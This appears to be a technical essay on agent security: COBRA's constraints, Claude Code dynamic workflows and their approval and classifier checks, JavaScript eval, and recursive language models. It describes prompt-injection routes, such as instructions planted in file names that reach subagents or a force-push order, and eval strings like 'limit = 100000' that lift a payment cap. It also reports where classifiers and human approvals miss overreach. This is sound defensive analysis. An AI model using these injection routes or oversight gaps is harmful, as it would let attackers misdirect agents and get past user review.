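COBRA's protection depends on whether a website has an approved sitemap. Without one, COBRA can only restrict which sites the agent contacts. In a test with WASP, a benchmark that uses copies of GitLab and Reddit, this restriction stopped the five attacks that contacted another site, but all 14 that misused the same site succeeded. With sitemaps, COBRA stopped all 19. Few websites publish such sitemaps, and some owners may not want to, for instance because they earn money from showing people advertisements. Zingrillo and colleagues wrote a tool that drafts sitemaps by crawling a site. Before any human corrections, its drafts contained every necessary operation for 18 of 25 web tasks.

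Some harmful actions look the same as harmless ones even when fully described. Two comments posted to the same page can differ only in whether the text is offensive. A compromised server can receive a proper tool call and do something else with it, as in 13 of the 1,223 cases in MCPTox, a benchmark of malicious tools. COBRA also covers only web requests and tool calls under the protocol, so it misses an email program sending mail through its own channel or a desktop application overwriting a file.

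COBRA also can't always check the price in the filter example, because some shops send only an item number at checkout and look up the price on the server. COBRA then has to rely on the price the model read from the screen, which an attacker would want to falsify.

### Whether limits on each branch are enough

Taken literally, data-flow integrity would stop the plan from reacting to the price, since the price comes from a page that COBRA does not trust. Information-flow proofs can establish that kind of separation, but the plan needs information from the page to shop. COBRA provides a weaker guarantee, under which content on the page may select a branch, but the branch may do only what its constraints permit.

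For the filter, this recovers most of what the reviewer cared about. If the order request includes the price, no permitted run can place an order above $50, so the review settles the price limit much as the range check did in the refund script. If the model wrongly decides against ordering, the user is left without a filter, which is only a nuisance.

A loan decision is harder to constrain. Suppose a bank employee asks the agent to approve an application if the documents are complete and to reject it otherwise. COBRA can limit both branches to that one application, so no run can approve somebody else's loan. But the request that approves the loan looks the same whether or not the documents are complete, so the constraints allow either outcome and the model that reads the screen still chooses between them. Meng and colleagues say their own system cannot prevent the misuse of actions that a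 policy deliberately permits. COBRA's constraints narrow this problem but don't remove it.

This suggests that, for each branch with serious consequences, a reviewer should ask whether the outgoing request would look different if the plan had taken that branch by mistake. If so, a constraint can catch the mistake. Otherwise, as with the loan, the plan should probably stop at that branch and ask the employee.

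### Who reviews constraints that a model wrote

COBRA's user approves the descriptions of sites and tools and supplies missing values. The planner model writes the constraints, and Zingrillo and colleagues describe no step at which a person reads them. In effect, the user approves the terms a plan can use, and a model decides which uses are allowed.

The planner writes the constraints before any hostile text can reach it, which reduces the risk, and COBRA achieved its results on STEER-Bench with constraints written this way. The greater danger is that the planner honestly misunderstands the user, because the same model writes both the plan and its limits. A user who asks the agent to spend at most $50 probably means $50 altogether. If the planner takes it to mean $50 per order, the plan and the constraint will agree, and both will be wrong. Meng and colleagues' system can count orders and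 allow only one, much as AWS's rules can count refunds, but only if somebody thinks to ask for it.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) treats this as an open research problem. When a model translates a request into formal rules and nothing validates the result, even perfect enforcement doesn't guarantee that the rules are the right ones. *ToolGuardian* (2026) makes a similar point about its own rule engine and recommends testing the rules on scenarios someone else wrote.

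Software can do part of the review. In *ActGov* (2026), a model only proposes policies, and a solver searches for any case in which they would break a fixed set of security requirements. The policies go into use only if the solver finds none. This check would catch a constraint that violates a company's standing rules, but not one that doesn't match what a user wanted on a particular day.

*Progent* (2025) uses a solver to decide when a person needs to review a policy change. A model writes the initial policy for a task and updates it during the run. Updates that only remove permissions take effect automatically, while the system can ask for approval of those that add permissions. In tests, only 6% of updates added any. On AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 39.9% of the time without a defence and 1.0% when the system accepted every update automatically. No attack succeeded when a person reviewed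 the initial policy and each expansion. A careful human reviewer can evidently improve on the model's policies, at least for AgentDojo's short tasks.

Meng and colleagues make the reviewer's task easier by having people write the policies in advance. A model only selects the ones a task needs and fills in values such as a spending limit. The user then sees the policies in plain language, including the numbers, and can change them before the run. The models chose the right policies more than 94% of the time in every category. They were less reliable when they also had to fill in the values, getting between 81% and 97% of 32 shopping tasks fully correct. A user who reads the dialog box can easily spot a wrong spending limit.

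It is doubtful that users would do this. In the permission experiment mentioned earlier, *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, one group wrote standing rules before the agent started. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, which postponed the decision until the run, and then approved 133 of the 199 overreaching actions referred to them. Their rules covered broad categories such as spending money, so people might do better with specific limits for a single errand. The survey *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* found that the most reliably enforced rules tend to be written in the notations that ordinary users are least able to read.

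A reviewer may not need to read the constraints branch by branch. Because they are in a formal notation, software could collect them into one list of everything the plan might send on any branch. Under the every-run reading, an approval authorises everything on that list. For the filter plan, the list would have two entries: place an order of at most $50 at this shop, or save the item for later. The user could check that quickly, and might notice that it doesn't limit the number of orders.

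## Scripts that launch agents: dynamic workflows in Claude Code

Dynamic workflows are a feature of Claude Code. The user describes a job, Claude writes a JavaScript program for it, and a runtime executes the program in the background. Unlike the program in a NOVA plan, which does the clicking itself, this program can't access files or websites directly. It starts agents that can, and gives each of them a task. Anthropic (2026) released the feature as a research preview in late May, and it is now generally available.

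Anthropic's *Introducing dynamic workflows in Claude Code* describes runs in which tens to hundreds of subagents work in parallel. Its main example is the port of Bun, a tool for running JavaScript, from the programming language Zig to Rust. One workflow worked out how long each piece of data had to stay valid, which matters in Rust. A second wrote the Rust files, with two reviewers for each file, and a repair loop then worked through the build and the tests. The port came to about 750,000 lines and took eleven days from first commit to merge, which is too large a job for anyone to approve one command at a time.

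Before dynamic workflows, Claude Code could already start subagents, and Claude chose the next one turn by turn. Anthropic's *A harness for every task* (2026), by two engineers who work on the product, explains why this works poorly on long jobs. Claude may stop after 35 of the 50 items in a security review and report that the job is done. It tends to favour its own findings when judging them, and it loses details of the original request each time it condenses a long conversation. A script keeps the loop, the conditions and the intermediate results outside the conversation.

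### Agents, pipelines and schemas

The function `agent()` starts one subagent with a prompt and returns its answer to the script. The subagent is a full Claude Code agent with its own tools, but it starts with a clean context and its only task is that prompt. `parallel()` starts several agents together and waits for all of them to finish. `pipeline()` sends each item in a list through one or more stages separately, so one item can reach the second stage while another is still in the first. Between these calls, ordinary JavaScript counts, filters and merges the answers.

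A subagent normally answers in prose, but the script can pass a schema that describes the form the answer must take, such as an object containing a list of strings. A schema is a type, like the refund script's whole number from 0 to 50, and the runtime checks the answer against it during the run. If the answer still doesn't fit after five attempts, the call fails. The model in the refund script could only answer, whereas a subagent uses tools before it answers, and the schema doesn't constrain what it does with them. For example, a subagent could delete a folder and then return a valid list of files.

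### Reading the audit-routes script

The feature's documentation, Anthropic's *Orchestrate subagents at scale with dynamic workflows*, includes a short script called audit-routes. It looks for missing authentication checks in a web application's routes, the pieces of code that respond to requests for particular addresses. With the JavaScript simplified, it reads:

```
found  = agent("List every .ts file under src/routes/.",
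               schema: an object with a list of strings, "files")

audits = pipeline(found.files, for each file:
               agent("Audit " + file + " for missing authentication checks."))

return audits, minus any empty results
```

The first statement starts one agent with a fixed prompt and a schema for the list it returns. The schema doesn't require the strings in the list to name real files or the list to be complete. It also allows an empty list, in which case the script would start no auditors and return an empty result. A hurried user could take that to mean that the routes have no problems.

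The second statement starts an agent for every string in the list. A reviewer can read the beginning and end of each prompt, but the first agent supplies the middle. Normally that will be a path like `src/routes/login.ts`, but the schema allows any string, including a sentence. Anyone who can add a file to the project can put an instruction in its name. The first agent might also open a file that contains a prompt injection and return the attacker's text as one of its strings. A bad answer in the refund script could cost $50, but one in audit-routes becomes part of the instructions to an agent with tools.

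The script also doesn't limit what the auditors do. An auditor that finds a missing check might go beyond reading the code and add the check, run the tests or install a package the tests need. Only the permission rules outside the script can stop it. The auditors have no schema either, so their findings can come back in any form.

The last line removes empty values from the results, which can hide missing results. An agent's result is empty if a user stops the agent or it hits an error it can't recover from. With 40 files and two crashed auditors, the script returns 38 findings and no sign that two routes went unchecked. A reviewer could ask for one more line that compares the number of findings with the number of files.

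The script could easily restrict the list of files further by accepting only strings that start with `src/routes/`, end with `.ts` and contain no spaces. It can't read the folder itself, but a saved workflow accepts input from the user, including a list of paths. If the user supplies the list, the first agent is unnecessary and every prompt is known before the run. The auditors' use of their tools would still be a deferred decision.

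### What the structure is good for

A longer example shows the gain over turn-by-turn agents more clearly. In *Orchestrate subagents at scale with dynamic workflows*, a tutorial with the same title as the documentation, Tuggle and Chan (2026) asked Claude for a workflow to fact-check a fictional company's letter to investors. The sources contradict four of the letter's ten claims and don't cover another two.

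Claude wrote a 152-line script. The request called for one agent to extract the claims and ten more to check one claim each and return "confirmed", "contradicted" or "unverifiable". Each "confirmed" verdict would then go to its own skeptic, an agent that tries to refute it, and a final agent would write the report. If the first agent returns ten claims as instructed, a script built this way starts 12 to 22 agents, depending on the number of "confirmed" verdicts. The run took two and a half minutes and cost $3.29.

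With turn-by-turn agents, Claude might skip the skeptics when the job gets long. A script's order of calls ensures that they run, and a reviewer can confirm this by reading it. This doesn't guarantee an accurate report, however, because the last agent writes it from the verdicts and could still describe a claim as confirmed after a skeptic had rejected it. Ordinary JavaScript could print the table of verdicts instead, leaving only the summary to the agent. Also, if a checker wrongly marks a true claim as contradicted, no other agent has the job of challenging that verdict.

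The loop in audit-routes has the same strength and a similar weakness. It starts an auditor for every file on the list, so the audit doesn't rely on a single agent that might stop at item 35 of 50. But an agent also made the list, and that agent could have stopped early and left files out.

A saved script runs the same stages each time, although its agents may answer differently. Claude Code disables the clock and the random-number function inside scripts so that a relaunched run repeats the same `agent()` calls. The script's next step therefore depends only on its input and its agents' answers, apart from any effects of the order in which the agents finish. This makes a script easier to review than a 213-line NOVA plan, because a reader can go straight to the `agent()` calls and trace where each answer goes.

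Other scripts fix less of their structure in advance. *A harness for every task* recommends a pattern in which a classifier agent identifies the kind of task and the script starts different agents depending on the result. In another pattern, the script keeps starting agents until they find nothing new. A reviewer can read the stopping condition, but the agents' answers determine when the script stops.

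A script can specify a model for each stage, such as a cheap one for extracting text, but it doesn't have to. If nothing else assigns a model, agents use the one the user's session is running. If an organisation has blocked the model a script specifies, Claude Code substitutes another. Anthropic also suggests letting an agent inspect the code first and then choose between two Claude models, Sonnet and Opus. A saved workflow could therefore run on a different model months after someone approved it, even if the script hasn't changed.

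### Limits on every run

The runtime starts at most 1,000 agents in a run and, by default, runs no more than 16 at once. audit-routes can therefore start one agent to list the files and at most 999 auditors. The limit stops a runaway loop from starting agents indefinitely, but it does little to limit harm, because it doesn't cap the number of commands each agent can run. In the fact-checking example, at most a couple of dozen agents made at least 56 tool calls.

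Other thresholds are only advisory. Claude aims for fewer than ten agents under the usual size setting, but a prompt can override this. If a run schedules more than 25 agents or its projected use passes 1.5 million tokens (the units of text users pay for), a warning appears but the run continues.

The script can't access files or the command line directly, but it can start an agent and tell it to run a command. The restriction is still useful because every outside effect has to go through an agent, and the session's permission rules apply to each agent. A rule that denies an action holds in every permission mode. If the user wants audit-routes to change nothing, a deny rule on editing is a much better guarantee than the word "audit" in the name, though the rule would also have to cover shell commands that write files.

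Retries need the same attention here as in the refund script. If an agent's output stalls for too long, the runtime restarts the agent from the same prompt, up to five times. The new attempt doesn't see what the old one did, and any files the old one changed stay changed. This hardly matters for an audit, but an agent that is supposed to email a customer might send the message twice.

### What the user sees before approving

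In the terminal, the approval screen shows the workflow's planned phases and lets the user run it, cancel it or view the raw script. The desktop app shows a card with the workflow's name, its phases and a caution about token use. A phase is a title that the script gives to a group of agents so that the user can follow their progress. The title doesn't restrict what the agents do, so a phase called "Audit" could contain agents instructed to edit. A script can also use a phase title that it didn't declare at the top, and a new group then appears in the progress view during the run. Audit-routes declares no phases, so the approval screen presumably shows little about it.

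A more useful screen would describe the `agent()` calls. For audit-routes, it could show that the script starts one agent with a fixed prompt, then up to 999 whose prompts contain text from the first agent, and that all of them can edit files under the current permissions. Software could probably determine most of this from a script this simple.

The session's permission mode determines whether the screen appears. In auto mode, a second model called the classifier reviews actions in place of the user. Ultracode is a setting that makes Claude plan a workflow for every substantial task. The table combines the workflow documentation with Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, which lists what each mode allows an agent to do without asking.

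| Permission mode | Approval before a workflow starts | What runs without a prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Manual | Every run, unless the user has waived it for that workflow | Reading files |
| Accept edits | Every run, unless the user has waived it for that workflow | Reading and editing files, common file commands |
| Auto | First launch only, or never with ultracode on | Anything the classifier lets through |
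| Bypass permissions | Never | Almost anything |

Other software can also start Claude Code through a command or a programming interface. These runs never show the screen, and permission rules determine whether the workflow may start. Tuggle and Chan launched their workflow this way, with a rule that allowed workflows, and read the 152 lines after the run finished.

Anthropic has since made auto mode the starting mode for terminal and VS Code sessions on every subscription plan, so the second-to-last row of the table is now the usual case. The first time a user says yes, Claude Code records consent in that user's settings, and later workflows start without a prompt. The consent covers scripts that Claude hasn't written yet. Under the every-run reading, it can't count as approval of a plan, because there is no plan yet whose runs anyone could examine, so it is closer to permission to use the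 feature.

In the manual and accept-edits modes, the user can waive the approval request only for a named workflow, such as a saved one, and only within one project. This waiver is narrower, but it still applies to a name rather than a particular text. Projects can share saved workflows, so a colleague might edit the script and keep the name. Anthropic's documentation describes no new approval request after such an edit. A stored fingerprint like COBRA's would work for scripts too.

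Even a user who read both the script and the documentation could have misjudged what the agents could do. According to the original documentation, workflow agents always ran in accept-edits mode, whatever the session's mode. The security company PromptArmor tested this and reported in *Claude Dynamic Workflows Inaccurate Permissions Docs* that the agents inherited the session's mode. In a session that bypassed permissions, agents that the user believed could only edit files could also run any command. Anthropic has since changed the description.

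### Why an approved prompt is not a request

In auto mode, the classifier is meant to block dangerous actions that the user hasn't asked for. It has to distinguish the user's instructions from others, which is difficult inside a subagent. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the instruction from whatever launched the subagent appears where the user's message normally would. Any task would then look fully authorised to the classifier.

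Claude Code therefore marks the prompts that a script passes to its agents as text the script computed, and the classifier doesn't count them as requests from the user. Suppose one of the file names in audit-routes contains an instruction to force push, which would overwrite the project's history on the server. The auditor might obey, but the classifier won't treat its prompt as the user's permission. The classifier also checks each subagent's task before it starts, its actions as it runs, and its work at the end. If the final review finds something suspicious, the report still goes back with a warning attached.

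The rule also applies to prompts with no inserted text. A user might open the raw script, see that an agent is instructed to force-push a named branch, and select "Yes, run it". On the every-run reading, this user has authorised the push. In auto mode, the classifier may still block it because the user hasn't asked for the push in a message.

That seems a sensible default if most people never open the script, but the few who do have to repeat in the chat what they have already approved. A finer rule could distinguish words that appear literally in an approved script from words that an agent supplied during the run. Meijer's checker already tracks data through a workflow in this way.

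### Signing off between stages

A workflow can't stop partway through to ask the user a question. It pauses by itself only when an agent needs permission for an action or when the user reaches a usage limit. Anthropic advises users who want to approve the work between stages to run each stage as a separate workflow.

For the route audit, the first workflow would return the list of files. The user could add a missing file, remove any entry that is a sentence rather than a file path, and pass the corrected list to the second workflow. In the second review, the user would then be approving a known list of files, which wasn't available at the first review. This is a large improvement, but the user has to be there when the first workflow ends, and one attraction of the feature is that it can run for hours unattended.

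Splitting the work into several workflows doesn't by itself ensure that the user is asked to approve each one. In auto mode, the second workflow starts without a prompt if the user has agreed to any earlier one. With ultracode on, Claude may run one workflow to understand the code, another to change it and a third to verify the change, all for a single request. Users who want to be asked can switch to manual mode. A permission rule that requires a prompt for the workflow tool should also work, since auto mode respects such rules. Telling Claude to wait for a review is less reliable, because the classifier relies on the instruction being in the conversation, and Claude Code can drop it when condensing the text.

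### How closely people look

There seems to be no published figure for how often users open the raw script. The nearest evidence is that users approve 97% of permission prompts but reject 39% of the written plans that Claude presents for approval, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

The gap between the approval rates for commands (97%) and plans suggests that people engage more with a readable plan than with a command. It doesn't prove that they approve commands carelessly or check plans for danger, because most of the commands are probably harmless and users also reject plans when they want a different approach. A workflow's approval screen is for reviewing a plan, but it looks like a permission prompt, and users must take an extra step to see the detail.

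Anthropic also directly tested whether people notice danger. It hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers had less to lose than real users because they weren't working on their own projects, and Anthropic was making the case for auto mode, but the difference is too large for either point to fully explain.

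Developers who review code carefully don't appear to be more careful about approving actions. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of those who said they carefully reviewed most or all of the code their agents wrote, 61% also said they often approved at least one type of action without close review. Among the other respondents, 67% said so, a difference that could easily be due to chance. The answers are self-reported, and the sample doesn't represent developers in general. A workflow script needs both kinds of review, and a developer who checks the JavaScript for bugs may never check what the agents it starts are allowed to run.

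Even an attentive user can't always tell from an approval prompt what they are approving. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents harming files and found that inadequate user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, the user had set the agent to proceed without asking. In 31, the prompt didn't make the effects of the command clear. For example, approving a routine-looking request to run `python3 setup.py` authorises whatever code the file contains. A list of phase titles similarly doesn't make clear what a workflow will do.

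For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115. They warn designers against treating repeated approvals as a stable preference, because people may just be tired of answering. Claude Code records consent for workflows after a single yes, which is even weaker evidence of a stable preference.

The classifier does much of the checking that this consent removes, and for single commands it is apparently better at it than a tired person. It isn't designed to detect that an audit has missed half the routes. It also has trouble judging what a user has agreed to. When Anthropic tested an earlier version on 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond its instructions, that version let 17% through. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had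 said or approved earlier as permission.

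## Running strings as code: the record of JavaScript's eval

When a user approves a dynamic workflow, the script is complete, even though its agents will choose their own commands. Other programs are incomplete at review because they build a string during the run, or receive one from elsewhere, and then run it as code. In JavaScript, the `eval` function does this. Python, Ruby and Lisp have similar functions, and a plan that executes whatever code a model returns relies on the same mechanism. Web programmers used `eval` long before language models could write programs, and researchers have recorded what they used it for.

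Three lines show the difficulty for a reviewer:

```
limit = 50
eval(text)
if (amount <= limit) pay(customer, amount)
```

Without the second line, no payment could exceed $50. But JavaScript runs the string as if it were written at that point in the program, with access to the same variables. If `text` is `limit = 100000`, the third line will allow almost any payment. Like the generated code in the refund script, the string could also call or replace `pay`, and a reviewer who doesn't know what the string contains has to consider all these possibilities.

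An automatic checker has the same problem. If a model returns a whole number from 0 to 50, the checker has to track one unknown value. After an `eval`, it has to assume that the evaluated code may have changed any variable within reach and redefined any function, including some built into JavaScript.

### What websites put in the strings

Researchers who built such checkers often ignored `eval`, or assumed that programmers used it only to read data and occasionally load a library. Richards, Hammer and colleagues tested these assumptions on the most popular websites of the time in *The Eval that Men Do* (2011). They modified Safari's browser engine to log every string that reached `eval`, where it came from and what the resulting code did.

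They made three sets of recordings in March 2011. For the first, they browsed the top 100 sites by hand for one to five minutes each, logging into accounts as a visitor would. For the second, the browser opened each of the top 10,000 sites and recorded for 30 seconds. The third added random clicks, at most one a second.

| | Browsing by hand | Page loads | Random clicks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sites visited | 100 | 10,000 | 10,000 |
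| Sites using `eval` | 82% | 50% | 52% |
| Calls to `eval` | 7,078 | 158,994 | 384,286 |
| Strings shorter than 64 bytes | about two thirds | 85% | 80% |
| Strings that fit no common pattern | 18% | 29% | 33% |

The 50% and 52% figures may count more than `eval` itself, because Richards and colleagues say they often use the word for a family of features that run strings, such as timers that accept code as text. In the same paper's breakdown by mechanism, `eval` appears on only 23% of sites in the page loads and 31% with random clicks.

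Most of the strings were tiny, with a median of four operations, such as reading a property or calling a function. JSON data, sometimes wrapped in an assignment or a function call, made up 37% of the strings from browsing by hand and 22% of those from random clicks. JSON borrows JavaScript's notation, so running it as code was a quick way to read it, and JavaScript had only recently gained a dedicated function for doing so.

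Other strings did not need `eval`. A script on the German news site heute.de checked which version of the Flash plug-in a visitor had. It stored the version number, set ten variables, `flash2Installed` through `flash11Installed`, and then used `eval` in a loop to read them back and recover the same number. The BBC's site ran a string that raised an error and immediately caught it, which had the same effect as writing `v=4`.

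The strings were also fairly predictable. Richards and colleagues sorted them into nine common patterns and a remainder. Of about 28,000 places in the code that called `eval`, only 399 (1.4%) received strings from more than one of these categories. That figure makes the calls look a little more regular than they were, because a place that ran only once couldn't vary and the remainder grouped different kinds of strings together.

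Among the strings in the simpler patterns, between 66% and 82% were constants, meaning text written literally in a script, or combinations of constants and basic values. But a reviewer could not necessarily have read these constants before the program ran. Google's home page, for example, fetched new scripts from a server during the visit, and the study counted the JSON text inside them as constant because it appeared literally in those scripts.

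### Replacing eval with ordinary code

Richards and colleagues judged that ordinary language features could replace most calls in the simpler patterns, which account for 76% of the strings collected by browsing by hand. That share must be lower in the two larger sets, at most 69% and 65%, because more of their strings fit no pattern. They had hoped to show that programmers could do without `eval`, but concluded that the data didn't support this. Some programs generate code for purposes that no existing feature covers. Many strings also referred to a function's local variables, which JavaScript can look up by name only through `eval`.

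A typical replacement turns `eval("foo." + x)` into `foo[x]`. If `x` is "price", both read the `price` property of `foo`. If `x` is "price = 0", the first version sets the price to 0, while the second looks for a property named "price = 0" and finds nothing. The second version is safer because the string can only name a property. For the same reason, a tool can't make the change without knowing what `x` might contain.

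Jensen, Jonsson and Møller automated such replacements in *Remedying the Eval that Men Do* (2012). They wanted other analysis tools to be able to read web applications, so the replacements had to be sound, meaning that the new program behaves as the old one did. In the example above, their method must establish from the rest of the program that `x` can only be a plain name. The method transforms many common uses of `eval`, but no such method can translate a library that the page downloads during the run, because the library's text is not available beforehand.

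*Eval begone!*, a follow-up to the 2011 study by the same research group, presents Evalorizer, a tool that helps a programmer remove unneeded `eval` calls. The researchers used it to remove `eval` from a real website. A programmer can accept replacements that a sound tool must rule out, for example by deciding that nobody meant `x` to change the price.

Removing every call to `eval` would still leave other ways to run new code. In the 2011 recordings, the search site ask.com passed 3.77 KB of text to `eval` and 1.39 MB to the whole family of features that run new code. Most of that 1.39 MB was libraries that scripts loaded by adding script tags to the page. One advertising agency's script loaded further scripts, which loaded others.

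### The browser's switch

Browsers now let a site turn `eval` off. The site can do this through Content Security Policy (CSP), a set of rules it sends with a page for the visitor's browser to enforce. CSP mainly defends against cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets their own code to run in a page that other people visit. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, lists control over `eval` among its goals. It recommends CSP as an extra layer of defence, since a site still needs to handle its input carefully.

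If a site's policy restricts scripts, the browser blocks `eval`, the similar `Function` constructor and timers given code as text. A site that needs these features can add the keyword `unsafe-eval` to its policy, according to MDN's *CSP*, a page in a reference work for web developers. Every script on the page can then run any string as code.

Most sites still permit `eval`. Report URI's *10 years of watching the web*, from a company that sells CSP monitoring, reports a crawl of 819,002 popular sites on 13 June 2026. Of these, 170,057 had a policy, and 71,094 of the policies (41.9%) contained `unsafe-eval`. The other 98,963 sites with a policy made up 12% of the total. The share that blocks `eval` must be smaller, because a policy that doesn't mention scripts doesn't block `eval`. Web Almanac's *Security* chapter for 2025 finds that the most common policies only require encrypted connections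 or control which sites may embed the page. Among policies that use keywords to restrict scripts, 77% include `unsafe-eval`. None of these figures measures how many sites still call `eval`.

One reason sites leave the switch on is that removing an exception can break them. Report URI makes this point about a related keyword, `unsafe-inline`, which a site can safely remove only if its owner knows every script written into its pages, including those from other companies. The same probably applies to `unsafe-eval`. If one script out of 50 needs `eval`, the site has to allow it for all of them.

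Google is testing a narrower permission in Chrome. *Extending supported hashes in script-src* (Ibarra Lopez and Acer, 2025) describes how a site can list a hash, a short fingerprint, of each string that `eval` may run. The browser runs those exact strings and blocks all others. To compile the list, the site can first use a mode that reports the hashes without blocking anything. This is advance approval in the strictest sense, and it would work for heute.de, whose loop only ever produced nine strings. It wouldn't work for JSON from a server, because each new value changes the hash, though a function that reads JSON could handle all of it safely.

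There is little evidence yet of how well this works in practice. Chromestatus's *Intent to Extend Experiment* records that the trial was extended to Chrome 150 because two bugs had kept the Google team that planned to test the feature from using it. The makers of Firefox and Safari had not taken a position.

### Whether a model's code is as predictable

The designers of some agents probably ask a model for code when they need much less, as the programmers at heute.de did. Suppose the refund script runs a model's code for each ticket, and in several hundred logged runs the code always works out a sum and calls `pay` once. The designer could ask for only the sum and restore the range check. The engineers at Imprint did something similar when they turned a prompt into a fixed script. Their experience suggests that a model often improvises steps that somebody could have written down once.

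However, the log alone would not guarantee that future strings are safe to run. The recordings from 2011 show what websites did in ordinary use, and an attacker using prompt injection would try to produce a string that no ordinary run contains. Reading JSON with a dedicated function is safer because the function never runs the text as code. A regular log is therefore a good reason to replace the open call with something narrower rather than approve it as it stands.

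A model's code is also harder to predict from the surrounding program than the strings were in 2011. Fixed lines of code assembled many of those strings from pieces already in the program, so a patient reader could often have listed the possibilities. A scaffold that requests code from a model contains the request but no pieces of the code that will come back. The resulting programs can also vary widely, as the NOVA plans for a single task did. Comparing their steps may overstate the differences that matter, since two plans can use different menus to order the same water filter. But to discount such differences, a designer would have to sort the programs by their effects, which is much harder than the text matching that sorted the strings in 2011.

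Agent designers also often have better reasons for using generated code. Much of the `eval` on the web came from programmers who misunderstood JavaScript, whereas an agent may need new code because nobody knows what the job involves until the data arrives. The closest counterpart to such code in the 2011 recordings is probably the 18% to 33% of strings that fit no pattern. Richards and colleagues inspected these by hand and found that the code did many different things.

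The JavaScript findings don't even carry over to every other programming language. In *What We Eval in the Shadows*, Goel, Donat-Bouillud and colleagues (2021) analysed 49 million calls to `eval` in R, a language for statistics. They found that R code used `eval` more widely, and arguably more dangerously, than earlier work had reported for JavaScript.

The lesson therefore seems to hold for small, repetitive jobs, such as picking fields out of a table, but much less for jobs in which the model has to work out the method. A fingerprint doesn't help on the first run of those jobs because the code doesn't exist yet. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) instead has a compiler check each new piece of code just before it runs.

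If the job repeats, someone can review the code from the first run before the second, save it, and allow later runs to execute only that code. The saved code may fail when the data changes. The plan should then stop for another review rather than let the model write and run a replacement.

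## Recursive language models: a short fixed loop that writes its own strategy

A recursive language model normally runs code that nobody has reviewed. Its fixed program is a loop of about ten lines, and a model writes everything the loop runs. Zhang, Kraska and Khattab (*Recursive Language Models*, 2025) designed this approach for inputs too long for a model to read at once. GPT-5, the main model in their experiments, accepts at most 272,000 tokens, and on harder tasks its answers get worse long before an input reaches that size.

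The design keeps the input out of the model's prompt. It stores the text as a variable called `context` in an interactive interpreter, a Python session that runs one block of code at a time and keeps its variables between blocks. The model first receives only a short description of the variable, such as its length, and has to write code to look inside. Simplified, the loop is:

```
session = start_interpreter(context=long_input, llm_query=ask_another_model)
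history = [short_description(session)]
while session has no final answer:
    code    = ask_model(history)
    output  = run(code, session)
    history = history + [code, beginning_of(output)]
return the final answer
```

The function `llm_query` lets the generated code send a prompt to another language model and keep the reply in a variable. A few lines of code can therefore send a query about each of 3,000 passages, whereas an agent that delegates in prose has to write out every request. The code can also assemble an answer too long for any model to write in one go.

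A depth setting limits the recursion. At depth 0, the code can't call a model, and at depth 1 it can call ordinary models. At depth 2 it can also start a second copy of the loop, with its own interpreter, on part of the input.

### A run in three rounds

Zhang and colleagues trace a run in which GPT-5 answers a question from 1,000 documents totaling 8.3 million tokens. The question describes a vegetable stew made with fish and a salty condiment, and a town with a yearly celebration named after the stew. GPT-5 has to find who won the beauty pageant at the thirteenth celebration.

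In the first round, GPT-5 wrote a keyword search and ran it over all the documents. The keywords included "beauty pageant", which came from the question, and "dinengdeng", "bagoong" and "La Union", which did not, so GPT-5 had evidently guessed that the stew was Filipino. The code printed the text around each match and called no other model.

One match looked promising. In the second round, GPT-5 wrote code that sent the matching passage to an inner model, stored the reply in a variable called `answer6` and printed it. The reply named Maria Dalmacio as the likely winner.

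The third round included two more calls to check this. The first extracted the year, the pageant and the winner's full name from the same article, and the second shortened the name in that reply to first and last. GPT-5 then returned "Maria Dalmacio", which was correct. The whole run cost 7.9 cents.

Nobody could have read the search terms, the choice of article or the three inner prompts before the run. GPT-5 had read text from the documents by the time it wrote the second block, so an instruction planted next to the word "bagoong" could influence the code that follows, as with an email agent that plans in rounds.

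The same loop can also waste good work. Qwen3-Coder, a large open model, had to list all pairs of users who had asked certain kinds of questions. It used inner calls to classify the questions and ordinary code to build the pairs, and soon had a complete list in a variable. But it failed to submit the list, so it started over several times. Finally it wrote out a different answer, which was wrong, and the run cost $1.12.

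### Scores and costs

The main experiments use four tasks. CodeQA has multiple-choice questions about code repositories, and BrowseComp+ has questions like the one about the stew. In OOLONG, the model must label a long list of short questions by type and compare the totals. In OOLONG-Pairs, it must find every pair of users that meets a condition, so the work grows with the square of the input's length.

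The table gives scores out of 100 for GPT-5, with GPT-5-mini answering the inner calls. The brackets show the average cost of a run and its standard deviation. The compaction agent summarises what it has read whenever its prompt fills up. OpenCode is a coding agent, which in this test reads the input from a file.

| Method | CodeQA | BrowseComp+ | OOLONG | OOLONG-Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 alone | 24.0 ($0.13 ± 0.07) | 0.0 (input too long) | 44.0 ($0.14 ± 0.02) | 0.1 ($0.16 ± 0.10) |
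| Compaction agent | 58.0 ($1.31 ± 1.46) | 70.5 ($0.57 ± 0.10) | 46.0 ($0.13 ± 0.01) | 0.1 ($0.13 ± 0.09) |
| OpenCode | 64.0 | 94.0 | 52.0 | 4.8 |
| Loop, depth 0 | 58.0 ($0.18 ± 0.56) | 88.0 ($0.44 ± 0.90) | 36.0 ($0.37 ± 0.42) | 43.9 ($0.69 ± 1.16) |
| Loop, depth 1 | 62.0 ($0.11 ± 0.10) | 91.3 ($0.99 ± 1.22) | 56.0 ($0.43 ± 0.85) | 58.0 ($0.33 ± 0.20) |
| Loop, depth 2 | 66.0 ($0.15 ± 0.30) | 92.0 ($0.55 ± 0.69) | 56.5 ($1.10 ± 3.25) | 65.5 ($0.33 ± 0.44) |
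| Loop, depth 3 | 58.0 ($0.15 ± 0.27) | 92.0 ($0.51 ± 0.54) | 58.0 ($0.51 ± 0.54) | 76.0 ($0.39 ± 0.32) |

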